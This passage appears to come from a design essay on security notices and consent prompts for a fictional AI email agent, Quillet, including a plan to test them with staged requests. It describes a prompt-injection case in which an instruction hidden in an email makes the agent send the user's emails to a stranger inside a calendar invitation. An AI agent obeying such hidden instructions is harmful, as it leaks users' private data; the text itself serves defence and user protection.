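The promise about asking covers only email. Quillet can also send data out another way, so the better-sounding "Nothing leaves without your approval" would be false.

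**When the user connects a mailbox:**

> Quillet will be able to read your last 30 days of email, except sign-in codes and password resets. If an attack gets past our safeguards, a stranger could steal anything Quillet can read. You can leave out folders now or later.

The buttons are "Connect 30 days", "Choose folders" and "Not now". Sign-in codes deserve special treatment because a thief could use them to get into the user's other accounts.

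**Before a risky action:**

> Send "passport.pdf" to bookings@harbour-inn.example? You have never written to this address, and its first email to you arrived today. You asked Quillet to "confirm my hotel for Friday". You can't take the file back after sending it.

The buttons are "Don't send", "Show their email" and "Send once". This request might be genuine, since some hotels ask for a passport. Quillet can't verify this, but the user may know whether they booked a room there and can phone the hotel to check. The software writes the prompt, so a hijacked model can't change the wording.

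**After a flaw is fixed**, to everyone who had connected a calendar while it was open:

> From 11 January to 3 March, a hidden instruction could make Quillet copy your email into a calendar invitation and send it to a stranger without asking you. Quillet now asks you before it sends any invitation, so this can no longer happen, but hidden instructions may still affect Quillet in other ways. We checked our full records of your account for those dates and found no stolen email. You don't need to install anything. You can review past invitations under Activity, or disconnect your calendar.

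The vendor can write "closes that route" because it added a fixed rule. A vendor that has only trained the model to resist the attack should write "makes this attack less likely to work".

**After an incident**, to the people whose records did show a theft:

> A stranger has three of your emails. Quillet sent them in a calendar invitation on 20 February at 10:32, because of an instruction hidden in another email. The emails contained a payslip, your tenancy agreement and a letter from your bank. We can't get them back. Tell your bank today that someone has your account number. If anyone contacts you and mentions these documents, assume it's a scam until you have checked. You did nothing to cause this. We have disconnected Quillet from your mailbox, and our support team will help you with each step.

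This notice starts with the loss because a user may stop reading if it opens with "an update about your security." It lists the stolen documents because the user can't judge what to do without knowing what the stranger has.

| Moment | Fact conveyed | What the user can do | Default that makes the text less necessary |
|---|---|---|---|
| Before purchase | Hidden text can hijack the agent, and safeguards don't always stop it | Choose another product, or keep a sensitive mailbox out | The agent drafts replies but can't send them |
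| Connecting the mailbox | What a hijacked agent could read | Leave out folders, or decline | 30 days of email, without sign-in codes |
| Risky action | This file is about to go to a new address | Refuse, or check with the hotel | The agent can't attach files to emails to new addresses |
| After a fix | One route was open between two dates | Review invitations, or disconnect the calendar | The calendar stays disconnected until a task needs it |
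| After an incident | Which emails the stranger has | Warn the bank and watch for scams | A short period of readable email limits the loss |

Defaults that stop the agent from sending email or limit it to reading the last 30 days of email make it less useful. For example, it couldn't find last year's contract. After a theft, the incident notice is the only text that a default couldn't replace.

### Testing whether it works

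The vendor could test the first three texts on new customers by randomly assigning visitors to the sales page to one of four groups. Two groups would see the Quillet texts and two would see ordinary permission screens. Within each pair, one group would get the cautious defaults in the table and the other would get looser ones. This would separate the effect of the texts from the effect of the settings. Google similarly separated text from design when it tested its certificate warnings.

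A week later, everyone would answer a few questions, such as "If you never open a stranger's email, can it still affect what Quillet does?" The correct answer is yes. The wrong answers should come from mistakes people made in earlier interviews, as they did in the second phase of the coupon experiment by Emami-Naeini and colleagues. If the wrong answers were all obvious, people could score well without understanding the risk.

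The vendor could count from its records how many accounts and folders people connected, and how many they later disconnected. The texts would be working if people who said at sign-up that they keep sensitive records in their email left those records out, while other people connected about as much as before. Fewer connections overall isn't automatically a better result.

To measure correct refusals, the vendor would occasionally show a staged request, such as one to send a file to an address the vendor controls, and make sure nothing left the mailbox. Participants would have to agree to these tests at sign-up. The vendor could estimate mistaken refusals, which block something the user wanted, by counting refused actions that the user then carried out by hand and by asking a sample of users about the rest.

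Both kinds of refusal matter because genuine requests are much more common than attacks. Suppose the texts raise correct refusals from 50% to 60% and mistaken refusals from 3% to 4%. A user whose agent sends ten emails a day would mistakenly refuse about 36 more a year. If that user faces one attack a year, the texts would stop an extra 0.1 attacks a year, or one for every 365 extra mistaken refusals. At a minute each, those refusals would take about six hours, which most people would accept to prevent the theft of their private email but might not accept to keep a newsletter from being archived.

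For the test to have an 80% chance of detecting a rise in correct refusals from 50% to 60%, the vendor would need about 385 people who are given the texts and 385 who aren't, each facing one staged request. Detecting a fall from 80% to 75% in the share who connect a mailbox would take about 1,090 people in each group. The vendor should count everyone in the group they were assigned to, even those who never read the texts, because people who read warnings may be more careful anyway.

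The vendor should repeat the questions and staged requests after six weeks, when the prompts have become familiar. Half the participants should not get a staged request until then. Otherwise, people who had already spotted one might do well because they expected another, and the vendor couldn't distinguish this from a lasting effect of the texts.

The last two texts need a different test, since it would be wrong to invent a theft or hide a real one from a control group. When a real flaw is found, the vendor could send everyone affected a full notice, randomly vary the wording, and compare how many people in each group reviewed their invitations, disconnected the calendar or called for help.
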